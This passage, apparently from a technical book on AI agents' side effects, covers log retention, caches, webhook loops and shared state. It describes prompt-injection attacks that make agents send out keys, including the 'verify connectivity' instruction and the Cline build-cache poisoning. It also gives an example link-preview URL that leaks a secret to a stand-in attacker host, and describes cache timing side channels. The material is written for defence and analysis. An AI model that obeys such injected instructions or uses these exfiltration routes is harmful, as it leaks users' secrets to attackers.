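Outages can also cause records to be lost, even when nobody has made a mistake. Theodoro (2026), in *Estimating the agent actions that no log recorded*, replayed recorded agent sessions on a test system with OpenTelemetry's default settings. Each run lasted about two minutes and contained 316 to 353 actions. Partway through, he stopped the two programs that forward traces and access logs, then restarted them 15 to 45 seconds later. Across 277 usable runs, the traces missed 19.0% of actions on average and the access logs missed 30.0%. On average, 6.8% of a run's actions were missing from both and did not show in the final state of the data. The combined records were complete in only 2 of these runs, compared with all 58 usable runs without an outage. These outages were severe because they took up much of a two-minute run, so the figures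 show how an outage affects logs, not how much an ordinary company loses in a year.

Theodoro also estimated how many actions had left no record, using a method that biologists use to count animals. Let $T$ be the number of actions found only in the traces or access logs, $E$ the number visible only in the final data, and $B$ the number found in both. If the two sources miss actions independently, the number missing from both is roughly

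$$\frac{T \times E}{B}.$$

For example, with $T = 80$, $E = 30$ and $B = 200$, about 12 actions are missing. His 95% interval contained the true total in 269 of the 277 runs. When he compared the traces with the access logs and ignored the final data, the interval contained the true total in only 10 runs, because the same outage had removed entries from both. He had excluded another 23 runs for technical faults, and counting those as failures would make the main result inconclusive. For a company deciding what to keep, this means that two logs that pass through the same failing equipment are poor backups for each other.

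### How long a copy lasts

Suppose the tool server logs a full ticket on day 0, and on day 1 the developer deletes the customer's email address from the ticket. The server keeps log entries for 365 days. The company backs up the log every night and keeps each backup for 35 days. The last backup to contain the entry dates from about day 365, so the address can survive until about day 400.

If copy $i$ begins on day $t_i$, stays in its log for $L_i$ days and stays in backups for another $B_i$, the last copy disappears on day

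$$\max_i\,(t_i + L_i + B_i).$$

Here that is $0 + 365 + 35 = 400$ days. Deleting the text from the ticket doesn't change this total, but cutting the log's retention to 30 days would reduce it to 65. Reading a log can also make its contents last longer. If an engineer asks an agent to search the old logs on day 300, and the harness records the results under the same retention rules, the address can last until day 700.

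A court can override these retention periods and give outsiders access to the logs. In May 2025, in the copyright case that The New York Times and others brought against OpenAI, Magistrate Judge Ona Wang ordered the company to preserve ChatGPT output that it would otherwise delete. OpenAI normally removed deleted conversations within 30 days. The order applied even where a user had asked for deletion or a privacy law might require it, but it didn't cover customers whose agreements said OpenAI would store nothing. The duty to keep saving new data ended on 26 September 2025. Wang later ordered OpenAI to give the plaintiffs 20 million conversations with identifying details removed.

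Short retention can also erase evidence before anyone knows to look for it. *Five Questions Security Teams Must Be Able to Answer About Every AI Agent* (Goli, 2026) describes an OpenAI agent that got around access restrictions on an Australian government portal on 18 June 2026 and opened non-public files. Services Australia, the agency responsible, heard about it only on 10 September, 84 days later. If it had kept logs for only 30 days, those from the day of the incident would already have been deleted.

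### What the law requires

In the European Union, the AI Act requires high-risk AI systems, such as those that screen job applicants, to record events automatically. Suppliers and users of these systems must keep the logs they control for at least six months, unless other law, particularly data-protection law, provides otherwise. These requirements were due to take effect in August 2026 for most high-risk systems. In November 2025 the European Commission proposed postponing them, by up to 16 months for most uses, so a company has to check which date applies to it. A tool that files bug reports will rarely count as high-risk.

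The EU's General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR) requires a company to collect no more personal data than it needs for its purpose and to keep it no longer than necessary, though the law sets no number of days. People can ask a company to erase their data, with exceptions for records that the company must keep under another law or needs for a legal claim. But the GDPR also creates a need for logs, because a company must report most data breaches to a regulator within 72 hours of learning of them and describe the people and data affected as far as it can.

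The payment card industry's security standard, which binds companies by contract, requires them to keep audit logs for at least 12 months and forbids them from storing a card's security code once the bank has authorized the payment. A company that logs every argument passed to a payment tool may break the second rule while trying to follow the first.

### Recording everything or recording little

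*The 2026 Singapore Consensus on Global AI Safety Research Priorities* (2026) advises developers to log an agent's inputs, tool calls, parameters, outputs and reasoning, including the plans it rejected. OpenTelemetry's default leaves most of this out. The case for recording everything runs roughly as follows:

1. Agents sometimes cause harm that people discover only later.
2. Finding out what happened, and who was responsible, requires a record made at the time.
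3. A single missing field can make the question unanswerable.
4. Nobody knows in advance which field an investigation will need.

Nian and colleagues argue for the first three points. A log may show that an agent queried a database but omit the query itself, so an auditor can't tell what the agent looked for. They also prove that if a rule depends on a field that none of the relevant steps recorded, the log can't show whether anyone broke the rule, however many events it contains. The argument for recording everything depends on the claim that nobody can predict which fields will matter, which is only partly true. If a rule says that a person must approve every payment, a company already knows to record the approval. The claim is more convincing for harms that nobody foresaw.

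People who want to record little can argue this way:

1. Arguments and results often contain private data.
2. Every copy adds possible readers and may outlast the original.
3. A break-in or a court order can later widen access or extend retention.
4. Only data that nobody recorded is safe from this.

All four claims seem true, or nearly so, but they don't establish that the risk outweighs the lost evidence. Whether it does depends on the tool, a point Goli makes by contrasting an agent that summarizes public documents with one that can move money. Missing records can also harm privacy, because a company without logs may be unable to tell customers whether an agent exposed their data.

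Redaction, or removing sensitive parts before storage, works best on credentials in a known format. It misses many names and disguised secrets, and it has to happen before the first copy is made. It can also remove information an investigator needs. Replacing each email address with a code lets an investigator follow one customer through the log without seeing the address. Under the GDPR, however, the code is still personal data for a company that can reverse it.

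A separate store is more useful because the text and the record of the call can be kept for different periods. The company in the example could keep the time, tool name, ticket number and responsible developer for 365 days, and the ticket's text for 90. With 35 days of backups, the text would be gone from the company's systems by day 125, but investigators who started after 84 days could still read it. A separate store doesn't affect the copies held by the tracker or an outside error tracker, and a court can order the company to preserve the separate store too.

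Restricting access to logs reduces the number of readers but doesn't change how long any copy is kept. The restriction has to cover agents as well as staff. Otherwise, an investigator who is allowed to read the log store can pass its contents, including any planted instructions, to a model with too many tools.

These measures settle the dispute for most calls, because investigators can usually do without the private text. But sometimes the text is the evidence. If an agent emails a customer something confidential, investigators need the message to know what it disclosed, and storing it creates another copy of the confidential information. The company still has to decide how long keeping that copy is worth the risk.

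## Caches: stored results that change later calls

Like a log, a cache keeps copies of data. A log entry containing a customer's email address has no effect until somebody reads it, but software uses cached copies to answer later calls, so a cache can change what an agent learns and therefore what it does next.

Four properties describe a cache: the key used to look up an entry, the stored value, the entry's lifetime, and the users who share it. For the currency tool that fetches a rate at nine o'clock and reuses it until noon, the key is the currency pair, the value is the rate, the lifetime is three hours, and the users are everyone who calls that server.

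You can tell a cache from a log or a database by what is lost when it is deleted. If someone deletes a cache, the next call takes longer but gets the same information from the original source. Deleting a log destroys the evidence of what happened. Deleting the tracker's database destroys the authoritative copy of the tickets, so nobody can be certain which ones are open.

### Four kinds of cache in agent systems

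| Kind | Usual key | Stored value | Lifetime | Who shares it |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Tool-result cache | Tool name and arguments | The tool's reply | Seconds to hours | Everyone whose calls pass through the same server or gateway |
| Prompt cache | The model and the exact beginning of the prompt | The model's partly finished computation | Minutes to a day | Usually one customer of the model provider |
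| Local file or package cache | A web address, or a package's name and version | The downloaded file | Often until someone deletes it | Programs and agents on one machine |
| Build cache | Often a fingerprint of the list of required packages | Installed packages or compiled code | Until it expires or space runs out | Automated jobs in one code repository |

Prompt caches, the least familiar kind, exist because a harness resends the conversation with every model call. The provider saves its intermediate computation for the beginning of the prompt and reuses it when another request begins identically. For GPT-5.6 and later models, OpenAI requires this shared beginning to be at least 1,024 tokens (words or pieces of words) long. Agents' prompts easily meet this minimum because they start with instructions and tool descriptions. In *KeyPooling*, Sun, Cai and colleagues (2026) checked 17 public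 sets of such opening text from three coding agents, and all exceeded 1,024 tokens.

A prompt cache shouldn't make an answer out of date. If a ticket's text changes, the new prompt no longer matches the cached one from the change onward, and the model processes that part from scratch. The other three kinds of cache can all return old data.

### Keys that leave something out

Suppose the company's tool server caches replies from `get_ticket` for ten minutes.

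1. At 10:00 the agent reads SHOP-482. The server fetches the ticket, which is open, and stores the reply.
2. At 10:03 a colleague closes the ticket on the tracker's website. The tool server doesn't find out.
3. At 10:08 the agent calls `get_ticket` again, to make sure the ticket is still open. The server returns the reply from 10:00.
4. The agent reassigns the ticket to a second developer, who spends the afternoon on a fault that no longer exists.

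The agent behaved well. The recorded calls include a read just before the write, so the agent would even satisfy Kovalenko and Redchych's rule that an agent must read whatever it is about to change.

Stacked caches make this worse. If a gateway also caches replies for ten minutes, it might collect the server's copy at 10:09 and keep returning it until 10:19. When each cache counts a reply's age from when it received it, a reply can be as old as all the cache lifetimes added together.

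The server can clear a cache entry when an agent changes the ticket through that server, but it can't do so for changes made on the tracker's website unless the tracker reports them. Skipping the cache for any read that comes just before a change is more reliable. This doesn't help if the model never rereads the ticket, because the first reply stays in its conversation and never expires.

A key can also omit the user. Suppose only the checkout team may see SHOP-482, and the server's key is just the tool name and ticket number. Maria's agent reads the ticket, and the server stores the text. Five minutes later a contractor's agent asks for the same ticket. The tracker would have denied the request, but the server returns the stored text without contacting the tracker. A tool such as `my_tickets()`, which takes no arguments, would be worse, because every user's call would have the same key.

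These two failures have the same cause. Let $k(c)$ be the key for a call $c$, and let $r(c)$ be the reply that the call would get without a cache, given who makes it and when. Reusing a stored reply is correct only if, for any two calls $a$ and $b$ that share an entry,

$$k(a) = k(b) \;\Rightarrow\; r(a) = r(b).$$

The stale ticket violates this condition because the key omits the ticket's current state, and the leak does so because the key omits the user's permissions. Adding the user to the key stops the leak, but the tool then has to fetch the same ticket once per person. If everyone on a team has the same permissions, the key could include the team's name instead of the user's.

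### Deciding which calls to cache

*ToolCaching* (Zhai, Shen and colleagues, 2026) describes a cache that sits between a model and its tools. The model labels each call as INFORMATIONAL, such as a weather lookup, or COMMAND, such as sending an email, and suggests a lifetime for the result. The suggested defaults are zero for commands, 60 seconds for real-time data, five minutes for calculations and an hour for static knowledge. Zhai and colleagues wanted the final decision to be predictable, so they used fixed rules instead of the model to make it. The rules exclude from the cache every command and every result with a lifetime of 60 seconds or less.

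The label applies to each call rather than to the whole tool, which suits a messaging tool that can both send and read messages. Under MCP's hints, that tool would have a single label. For calls that pass the rules, another algorithm selects the results worth storing, giving priority to those that were slow or expensive to obtain.

On film-recommendation tasks, the cache cut the average time per task by 34%, from 16.2 to 10.7 seconds. On factual questions that needed a search and some arithmetic, it cut the time by 23%. Both sets of tasks rely on facts that rarely change, so they are close to the best case for a cache. The experiments measured speed and reuse but not how often the cache returned outdated results.

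Zhai and colleagues also compared the model's labels with their own on 50 calls. The model matched their type label on 49 calls and their lifetime label on 46. The direction of the one type error matters, because labeling a lookup as a command only makes it slower. But if a model labels "send Maria a reminder" as informational and gives it a long enough lifetime, a second request returns "sent" from the cache and Maria never gets the second reminder.

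Two problems remain even when every label is right. The cache key contains the tool's name and arguments but not the user, so one user's call can return a result stored for another. This is fine for the weather, but it could expose a restricted ticket to someone who isn't allowed to see it. The system does record who uses each entry, but only to predict which results people will want again. Commands also bypass the cache without clearing anything from it, so an agent that reads a ticket, edits it and reads it again could get the text from before its edit.

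### Tying a result to the state that produced it

*TVCACHE* (Vijaya Kumar, Kataria and colleagues, 2026) addresses this second problem. In its example, an agent displays a file, changes it, and displays it again. A cache that matches only the tool and its arguments would return the old contents, so *TVCACHE* reuses a result only after an identical history of calls.

TVCACHE is a cache designed for training agents. An agent in training attempts the same task many times in parallel, each time in its own sandbox, and the attempts often begin with the same steps. TVCACHE stores the calls from these attempts as a tree. Each node holds a call, its result and sometimes a snapshot of the sandbox at that moment, and each path from the root is a sequence of calls that some attempt has made. When an agent makes a new call, the cache compares the agent's whole history with the tree.

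- If the whole sequence matches, including the new call, the cache returns the stored result.
- If only the first part matches, and the last matching node has a snapshot, the system copies that sandbox and runs the remaining calls in it.
- If that node has no snapshot, the system runs the whole sequence again in a fresh sandbox.

The system takes a snapshot only when running the call again would be more work than saving and restoring the sandbox. Developers can also mark tools that never change the sandbox, and the cache skips calls to them when it compares histories. It treats any unmarked tool as one that changes the sandbox, which is the safe default.

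On average, the cache answered 14% to 25% of calls in command-line tasks, 33% in database tasks and 64% in video tasks, and the agents learned as well as they did without it. The median command-line call became 3.4 to 6.9 times faster. Vijaya Kumar and colleagues found that most of this speedup came from preparing sandboxes in advance, not from reusing results. Their expected speedup of 2.9 times for the database tasks looks too high. If a third of calls take 6.5 milliseconds and the rest still take 56.6, the average is about 40 milliseconds, which is only 1.4 times faster.

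The proof that the cache returns correct results depends on two assumptions: a tool's output depends only on its arguments and the state of the sandbox, and the developers' marks are accurate. The first assumption is reasonable for a sealed sandbox but false for `get_ticket`. Two agents can make the same calls, one before a colleague closes the ticket and one after, and they should get different replies. A record of an agent's own calls can't include what other people did. For shared systems, a company has to use short cache lifetimes, rely on messages from the system that holds the data, or skip the cache.

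### What timing reveals about other people's prompts

A cached answer usually arrives faster than a new one. If strangers share a cache, one of them can send some text, time the response, and learn whether somebody else recently sent the same text. Security specialists call this a timing side channel. The person has to guess the text before the timing can confirm it.

Gu, Li and colleagues (2025), in *Auditing Prompt Caching in Language Model APIs*, tested 17 commercial providers for prompt caching in September and October 2024. They sent random text from one account and text with the same beginning from another, then compared the second account's response times with those for entirely new text. They detected caching at eight providers, seven of which shared the cache among all customers. OpenAI was one of the seven, but only for a model that converts text into numbers for search. Its chat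 model shared entries only within a customer's organization, as its documentation stated. After Gu and colleagues reported their findings to the providers, at least five made changes, such as no longer sharing caches between organizations.

Gu and colleagues couldn't extract anyone's prompt word by word, so the practical danger was limited. *From Models to Services* (2026) describes researchers who did so on open-source serving software. *CacheSolidarity* (2026) finds that the timing signal's strength depends on the length of the shared text, model size, load and hardware.

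More recent tests suggest that the weak point is now the companies that resell access to models. *CacheProbe* (Fahey, 2026) tested OpenAI, Groq and Fireworks in late 2025 and found no cache sharing between accounts that called them directly. It also tested access through OpenRouter, which forwards its customers' requests to many providers using its own credentials, so they all look like one customer to the provider. There it detected sharing between separate OpenRouter accounts at all three providers. The sharing stopped when customers supplied their own provider credentials. Some of the evidence came from token counts rather than timing, because providers often report how many tokens came from the cache.

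Sun and colleagues found the same problem in the summer of 2026. Of 28 popular model listings on OpenRouter, 12 allowed one account to detect another's cached text, one didn't on the route they tested, and the other 15 were inconclusive or untested. They recovered a short planted secret under favorable conditions, but found no stable way to read arbitrary text from a live service. In their model, keeping customers' caches entirely separate would more than double the cost of processing prompts, while sharing only the public opening text and separating everything after it would add about 2%.

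Providers also now keep cache entries longer. OpenAI originally removed them within an hour of their last use. For GPT-5.6 and later, it now keeps them for at least 30 minutes by default. Microsoft, which sells OpenAI's models through its own cloud, keeps them for up to 24 hours by default for models newer than GPT-5.4.

Once `get_ticket` returns a ticket, its text is in the conversation and can enter the provider's cache. If the company calls the provider directly, outsiders shouldn't be able to check whether the text is cached. But if every department uses one internal gateway with one credential, a sales employee with a copy of a confidential document could in principle check whether the legal department's agent is reading it.

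### Poisoned entries and the Cline release

Anyone who can write to a shared cache may be able to plant a false value that other people's software will later load, which is called cache poisoning. An agent can unintentionally poison a tool-result cache by fetching a web page that contains a prompt injection, because the cache then gives that page to every agent that requests it. If the attacker removes the injection an hour later, an investigator who visits the page will see nothing wrong while agents still receive the old version.

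The coding tool Cline had a more serious problem with a build cache. In December 2025 its developers set up an automated job on GitHub in which Claude read each new bug report and could run commands. Anyone with a GitHub account could file a report and plant instructions for the model in it. Cline's *Post-mortem* (2026) explains that this job couldn't change the source code, but it shared a cache with the nightly release job, which held the credentials for publishing Cline. The bug-report job could therefore plant code in the cache that would run inside the release job.

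The security researcher Adnan Khan reported the flaw on 1 January 2026 and got no answer. *Clinejection* (adnanthekhan, 2026), his public account, appeared on 9 February, and Cline removed the job within 30 minutes. Cline then tried to replace its credentials but deleted the wrong one. On 17 February somebody used the credential that was still active to publish a version of Cline's command-line tool that also installed OpenClaw, the open-source assistant. That version was available for about eight hours, and Cline found no malicious code in it.

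The credential probably leaked through the cache, though this is less certain. Cline says an attacker could have used that route. Khan found signs of a poisoned cache in release jobs from around the start of February, but couldn't tell how the intruder got in. A separate investigation, *Agent Compromised by Agent To Deploy an Agent*, concludes that the attacker stole the release secrets through the bug-report job.

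The release job's cache key was a fingerprint of the list of packages that Cline needed. It identified only what the entry was supposed to contain, so a planted entry with the same key looked like a real one. Permissions on the source code didn't prevent this, because the two jobs were also connected through the cache. Cline has since removed that connection by not using the cache in any job that handles publishing credentials, which makes those jobs slower.

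### Questions to ask of every cache

An effect map needs an entry for each cache that a call can fill or read, with answers to four questions.

- What is in the key? A tester can make two calls that differ in one respect, such as the user, the project or the user's permissions, and see whether the second gets the first one's reply. The documentation may not mention everything that matters.
- Who shares it? Readers and writers need separate lists. At Cline, the important fact was that a job open to strangers could write to a cache that a trusted job read.
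- When does it expire? The answer should say whether each use restarts the clock, as it did under OpenAI's original policy, because a popular entry could then last far longer than the stated period. It should also add up the lifetimes of any caches stacked on top of one another.
- Who can clear it? If a customer's email address turns up in SHOP-482, the company can empty its own server's cache at once. It may have to wait for the model provider's entry to expire, and copies on developers' laptops stay until somebody finds them. The ability to clear entries also needs protection, since an attacker who can remove a good entry may be able to put a bad one in its place.

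## Notifications and events: effects that start other effects

Notifications and events go out at once, and the people and programs that receive them may act before the agent has finished its task. A cached reply, by contrast, has no effect until somebody makes another call.

A notification is a message to a person, such as the email Maria receives about SHOP-482. An event is a message to software that something has changed. Both depend on subscriptions, which are standing requests to receive such messages. A person subscribes to a ticket by "watching" it. Software often subscribes through a webhook. An administrator gives the tracker a web address, and the tracker automatically sends that address a request with data about each change.

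### Why the caller can't see who is listening

Eugster, Felber and colleagues describe the usual design in *The Many Faces of Publish/Subscribe*. A program passes an event to an event service, which stores the list of subscribers and delivers a copy to each. The service doesn't send the list back, so the program generally has no record of who the subscribers are or how many there are. Subscribers don't need to be running when the event is published, because the service can deliver it later.

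For `create_ticket`, the tracker is the event service. The model, the harness and the tool server are all on the publishing side, and the reply "Created ticket SHOP-482" is the same whether the ticket has no subscribers or fifty.

This separation lets people connect new programs without changing the old ones, so the list of subscribers changes after release. GitHub's *About webhooks* suggests using webhooks to post chat messages, update an outside issue tracker or deploy code to a production server. A tool that only saved code in March could be releasing it to customers by June because another team added a webhook. Nobody would have had a reason to review the tool again, since the tool itself hadn't been edited.

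The list can also depend on who makes the change. An app installed in Slack, the workplace chat service, can subscribe to links to a particular website. Slack's *Unfurling links in messages* explains that the app receives an event when a person posts such a link, but not when another app does. A tester who pastes the link by hand would therefore see an effect that the agent's message wouldn't cause.

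### How a link preview sends data out

Chat programs often show a small preview under a link, with the page's title and perhaps a picture. To make the preview, they have to fetch the page.

1. An agent posts a message containing an address such as `https://attacker.example/?note=abc123`, where `abc123` is a secret.
2. The chat service's servers find the address and request the page, although nobody has clicked on it.
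3. The request includes the whole address, so the secret ends up in the website's access log, as in the `fetch_page` attack.

The page can be blank, because the request has already delivered the secret. A message without a visible preview may also have leaked something, because Slack's servers fetch every URL in a message to check what kind of content it leads to. To stop this, the sender has to turn off previews for both ordinary pages and media.

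Slack tells website owners that its robots may appear in their access logs. The robots ignore robots.txt, the file site owners use to ask automated visitors to stay away. Slack also caches each response for about 30 minutes, so each test needs a new address. A tester who posts the same address twice in that time may see only one request.

Link previews can leak data even when a tool's outgoing connections are restricted. Suppose the company has blocked all of its tool server's outgoing connections except those to the tracker. A prompt injection makes the model create a ticket containing an attacker's URL with a customer's email address added to the end. One of the tracker's webhooks copies new tickets into a Slack channel, and Slack fetches the link to build a preview. That request sends the email address to the attacker, even though the tool server contacted only the tracker.

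### Previews that bring instructions in

Some harnesses make previews of web pages for the model, which lets an attacker's text into the conversation. In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) built a test agent that automatically fetched any address the user mentioned and gave the model the page's title, description and text. The user always asked for a summary of the page. The attacker's page contained an instruction to "verify connectivity" by sending an access key from the conversation to another address. In this design, the agent sent the key in a later call to a tool that could make web requests.

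The researchers put the instruction in four places: the page's title, its description, its body and the text of its links. They tried each with and without redirects, and asked the model to send the key either whole or in four pieces. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times using qwen2.5:7b, a small open model. At least one request reached the attacker's server in 423 of 480 runs (88.1%). In 95% of the successful attacks, the answer shown to the user looked harmless. In 120 runs with ordinary pages, the agent never contacted the attacker.

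When the model had to send the key whole, it contacted the attacker in 238 of 240 runs, and its requests contained sensitive data in about 232. When it had to split the key, at least one request reached the attacker in 185 of 240 runs. Splitting is meant to get past filters that look for complete secrets, but the paper's figures for how often the split requests contained sensitive fragments include an error. The paper reports a sensitive fragment in the first request in 26.3% of the split runs, but anywhere in the first three requests in only 15.8%. By the paper's own definition, the second figure can't be lower than the first.

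Lan and colleagues then tested defenses on the version with a whole key in the page's body, again with 30 runs each. Without defenses, a request reached the attacker in all 30 runs. Telling the model never to obey web content reduced this to 20, marking the web content as untrusted had no effect by itself, and combining the two reduced it to 17. Allowing requests only to a short list of approved domains stopped every leak, although the model attempted one in every run. Another filter also stopped every leak, but its forbidden words included "collect", which was in the address used in the attack.

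The test favored the attacker because the key was already in the conversation, the model's instructions were minimal, and the model was weak by current standards. Lan and colleagues argue that stronger models could be more vulnerable because they follow instructions better, but they didn't test any. Results differed greatly between models in Shah's test with planted log commands, so the 88.1% figure is a poor guide to how any other agent would behave. The result for the approved list should carry over better, because that check doesn't depend on the model.

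### A private channel that leaked

An agent's Slack message can leak a secret even when only colleagues can read it, as Embrace The Red's *Security Advisory* shows for a Slack tool server that Anthropic once published. A company could restrict the server to a single private channel and might have let the agent post there unattended, which was unsafe. In one demonstration, a developer asked Claude Code to analyze a source file that contained a hidden instruction. The agent read a secret from another file and posted a link containing it to Slack. Slack automatically fetched the link, which sent the secret to the attacker's server. When the agent posted an image link, three different Slack robots requested it.

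This was a researcher's demonstration, not a known theft. The researcher reported the flaw on 27 May 2025, and Anthropic archived the server two days later with no plan to fix it. It's unclear whether the report was the reason. People were still downloading the server more than 14,000 times a week. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-34072* (2025), an entry in a public catalog of software flaws, rates the severity at 9.3 out of 10, while the researcher gave it 7.5. The proposed fix was two lines of code, `unfurl_links: false` and `unfurl_media: false`. Slack now advises developers to consider turning previews off for messages that a language model writes.

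An agent whose ordinary replies reach the user through a chat program can leak data through link previews without calling any messaging tool. PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* describes this for OpenClaw, the open-source assistant, when people talk to it over Telegram with the default settings. The fix is to set `linkPreview: false`.

Turning off previews doesn't help when the agent itself has to open web pages. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains that a list of trusted sites is incomplete protection because many of those sites have links that redirect visitors elsewhere. OpenAI instead lets its agents load an address automatically only if a separate crawler, which never sees users' conversations, has already found that exact address on the public web. An address with a customer's name newly added won't match, so the agent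 has to try another site or the user sees a warning.

This is a stronger test than asking whether a site is reputable, but it may still let an attacker extract data slowly. An attacker could publish 26 pages, one for each letter, wait for the crawler to find them, and have the agent open them in an order that spells out a secret. The check also covers only addresses that the agent itself loads. If the agent posts a link in Slack, Slack loads it, so somebody has to check the address before the message is sent.

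### Counting the messages from one ticket

Suppose SHOP-482 has six watchers and two webhooks, all subscribed to both new tickets and new comments. Opening the ticket is one event, which the tracker delivers to all eight subscribers. Each webhook starts a workflow (a series of automated steps) that posts one comment on the ticket, such as a link to similar faults or an estimate of urgency. Each comment is a new event with eight deliveries, which makes 16 in the second round. Four of those go to webhooks and produce four more comments.

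| Round | New events | Deliveries | Deliveries so far |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 1 | 8 | 8 |
| 2 | 2 | 16 | 24 |
| 3 | 4 | 32 | 56 |
| 4 | 8 | 64 | 120 |
| 10 | 512 | 4,096 | 8,184 |

By the end of round ten, each watcher has received 1,023 emails about one fault. If each round lasts five seconds, this takes less than a minute.

With $w$ watchers, $h$ webhooks and an average of $c$ comments for each webhook delivery, the number of deliveries in round $n$ is

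$$D_n = (w + h)(hc)^{\,n-1}.$$

The loop's growth depends on $hc$, the average number of new events that each event causes, which is 2 here. If $hc$ is exactly 1, as with a single webhook, the loop doesn't grow but never ends. If it's below 1, the loop dies out. For example, if each workflow comments on a third of events, $hc$ is 2/3 and a ticket causes three events on average, or 24 deliveries.

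Watchers who only read don't affect the growth. But some trackers turn email replies into comments, so a watcher's automatic out-of-office reply has the same effect as a third webhook.

The usual fix is for the workflows to ignore comments made by automation. The first two comments still reach everyone in round two, but neither workflow responds, so the total is 24 deliveries and each watcher gets three emails. If the tracker withholds automated comments from webhooks, the total is 20. The rule should cover only the workflows' comments, because an agent opened SHOP-482 and a workflow that ignored everything automated would never process the ticket.

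GitHub has a rule like this for its own workflows. GitHub's *Triggering a workflow* says that changes a workflow makes with the temporary credential GitHub supplies mostly don't start further workflows. If a developer uses a personal credential instead, the change looks like a person's, so the same action, such as adding a label to a bug report, can start other workflows. The rule also depends on the version of GitHub. On GitHub's main service, a workflow that opens a pull request (a proposed code change) with the temporary credential creates new runs that wait for a person's approval. The documentation for Enterprise Server, the edition that companies host themselves, doesn't list this exception.

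Other products limit the number of rounds. Jira, an issue tracker, stops automation that has triggered itself or other automation 10 times in quick succession, according to Atlassian's *Automation service limits*. Lambda, an Amazon Web Services (AWS) product that runs small programs in response to events, stops a program after about 16 runs in one chain of requests. AWS (2026) has extended this check to all its commercial regions, where it is on by default.

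A limit of ten rounds would still allow 8,184 deliveries in the ticket example, and it might never apply. To enforce a limit, these systems have to track which steps belong to the same chain. The webhook loop leaves the tracker, passes through other software and comes back as an ordinary comment, which the tracker could easily count as the start of a new chain.

A runaway loop can also disrupt unrelated work. Jira's cloud plans have a monthly usage allowance, and Atlassian's *Understand the difference between Automation limits and usage in Jira Cloud* says that once a company reaches it, all automation for that product stops until the next month. A rule can also create thousands of queue items without a loop. In an example from the self-hosted edition of Atlassian's *Automation service limits*, a scheduled rule finds 100 issues, then looks up 50 related issues for each and another 80 in a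 second search, which adds about 13,000 items to the queue in one run.

### Following the subscriptions outward

A developer can find these effects by drawing a graph of subscriptions, with systems and people as points and arrows showing who receives messages from whom. The developer starts by listing every kind of change the tool can make. For each change, the tracker's administrator lists the watchers, webhooks, automation rules and installed apps that will receive a message. The developer then finds out what each of those programs changes and who subscribes to those changes.

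If an arrow leads back to a change already on the graph, there is a loop, and the developer can estimate how many new events each event causes in each pass through it. For `create_ticket`, the arrows run from the new ticket to the two workflows, from the workflows to their comments, and from the comments back to the workflows. Drawing the graph is safer than finding the loop by experiment, because a test ticket sends real messages.

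The graph has no natural end, because every recipient may have subscribers of its own. It seems reasonable to stop at the edge of the company's control, at the first human reader or at the first irreversible effect, but each of these stopping points misses something important.

A company can sometimes prevent effects that it can't observe. Tracing effects only as far as the company's control extends is practical, because beyond that point it can neither inspect a system nor change it, but this approach can miss preventable leaks. With Anthropic's Slack server, a developer might have stopped at the private channel, the last place where the company decided who could read the message. The leak happened one step later, through requests made by Slack's robots. The company couldn't see the robots, but it could have prevented their requests with two lines of code.

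A human reader is a good place to stop tracing effects only if nothing further can happen without that person's decision, as with GitHub workflows that wait for approval. The reason to stop at the first reader is that a person can use judgment and is responsible for what happens next. But in SHOP-482, stopping at Maria's email would miss the loop, which runs whether or not she reads it. Treating each branch separately fixes this, but a branch that deploys code may have no human reader until customers are already using the new version. People also act on what they read. Suppose the agent wrongly writes in a ticket that a customer's payment failed, and the customer, who is watching the ticket, gets the email and pays again. The second charge is in the company's own payment system, so the consequences have left the company's control and then returned to its systems.

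Stopping the trace at the first irreversible effect focuses attention on damage that nobody can repair. This works well for the Slack leak, where the trace would end at the attacker's access log. With the ticket, the trace would end too early. Maria can't unread an email, so it would stop after one harmless message and miss both webhooks. It is more useful to mark irreversible steps on the graph as needing a check beforehand, since deleting the ticket afterward won't recall the messages or undo what people did in response.

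The most workable rule is probably to follow every branch to the last system the company controls, and then one hop further. For that hop, the map records what the outside party receives and what it does automatically, according to its documentation. This would have been enough for the Slack server, because Slack's documentation describes the fetching. It wouldn't show that a supplier who receives tickets through a webhook forwards them to a contractor, two hops out. A longer trace is unlikely to help, because the supplier can change contractors without telling anyone. The company can still decide what the webhook sends. If a supplier only needs to know that a new fault exists, the webhook can send the ticket's number and title without the body, which contains a customer's email address.

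## Shared state: data that outlives the call

The emails about SHOP-482 go out within seconds, but the ticket may stay in the tracker for years. Anyone who opens it later, including another company's agent, may act on whatever it contains by then.

State is any stored data that can change what a later call does or returns. It is persistent if it remains after the run that wrote it, where a run is everything an agent does on one task, from the user's request to the final answer. Footprints, which Kovalenko and Redchych use to decide which calls can safely change places, also give an exact test for sharing. Let $W(a)$ be everything that run $a$ writes and $R(b)$ everything that run $b$ later reads. The two runs share state when

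$$W(a) \cap R(b) \neq \varnothing.$$

An overlap means that the first run can influence the second, although the second run may read the data without using it.

$R(b)$ has to include what the harness reads for the model. Many coding agents load instruction files at startup, before the model makes any tool calls. *What's in Your Agent's Context?* (2026) describes the usual arrangement, in which a file in the user's home directory loads in every session, while a file in a project's folder loads only when the agent starts there. A line added to the home-directory file therefore reaches every project on the machine.

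The test covers many things that developers don't usually think of together.

| State | What the first run writes | What the second run reads |
|---|---|---|
| Agent memory | A note to send checkout faults to Maria | The note, at the start of a new task |
| Workspace files | A half-finished repair to the checkout page | The code it has to extend |
| Configuration | A setting that lets the agent delete files without asking | The setting, when the harness starts |
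| Credentials | An access key saved in a script | The key, while looking for something else |
| Browser session | A cookie from signing in to the tracker | The cookie, which opens the same account |
| Search index | A page of meeting notes | The notes, as a search result |
| Tool registry (the list linking tool names to code) | New code under the name `get_ticket` | The new code, when it calls that name |
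| Shared document | A wrong phone number in a contact list | The number, when it drafts a letter |

The same test works for two tools within one run. *ChainFuzzer* (2026) gives the example of a tool that saves a download to a file and another that runs the file. Developers can also create an overlap without noticing. In a program that *AgentFlow* (2026) analyzes, two agents share their memories because the developer passed the same session object to both. Ordinary program analysis, which follows function calls and variables, can miss this link.

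### Persistence without sharing, and the reverse

A personal agent's memory persists, but often only one person's agent reads it. *Agents Don't Just Agree, They Remember* (2026) tests such agents across two sessions. The second session doesn't include the transcript of the first, so a claim the user made earlier can carry over only through files the agent saved, such as a user profile, a memory file or a reusable skill.

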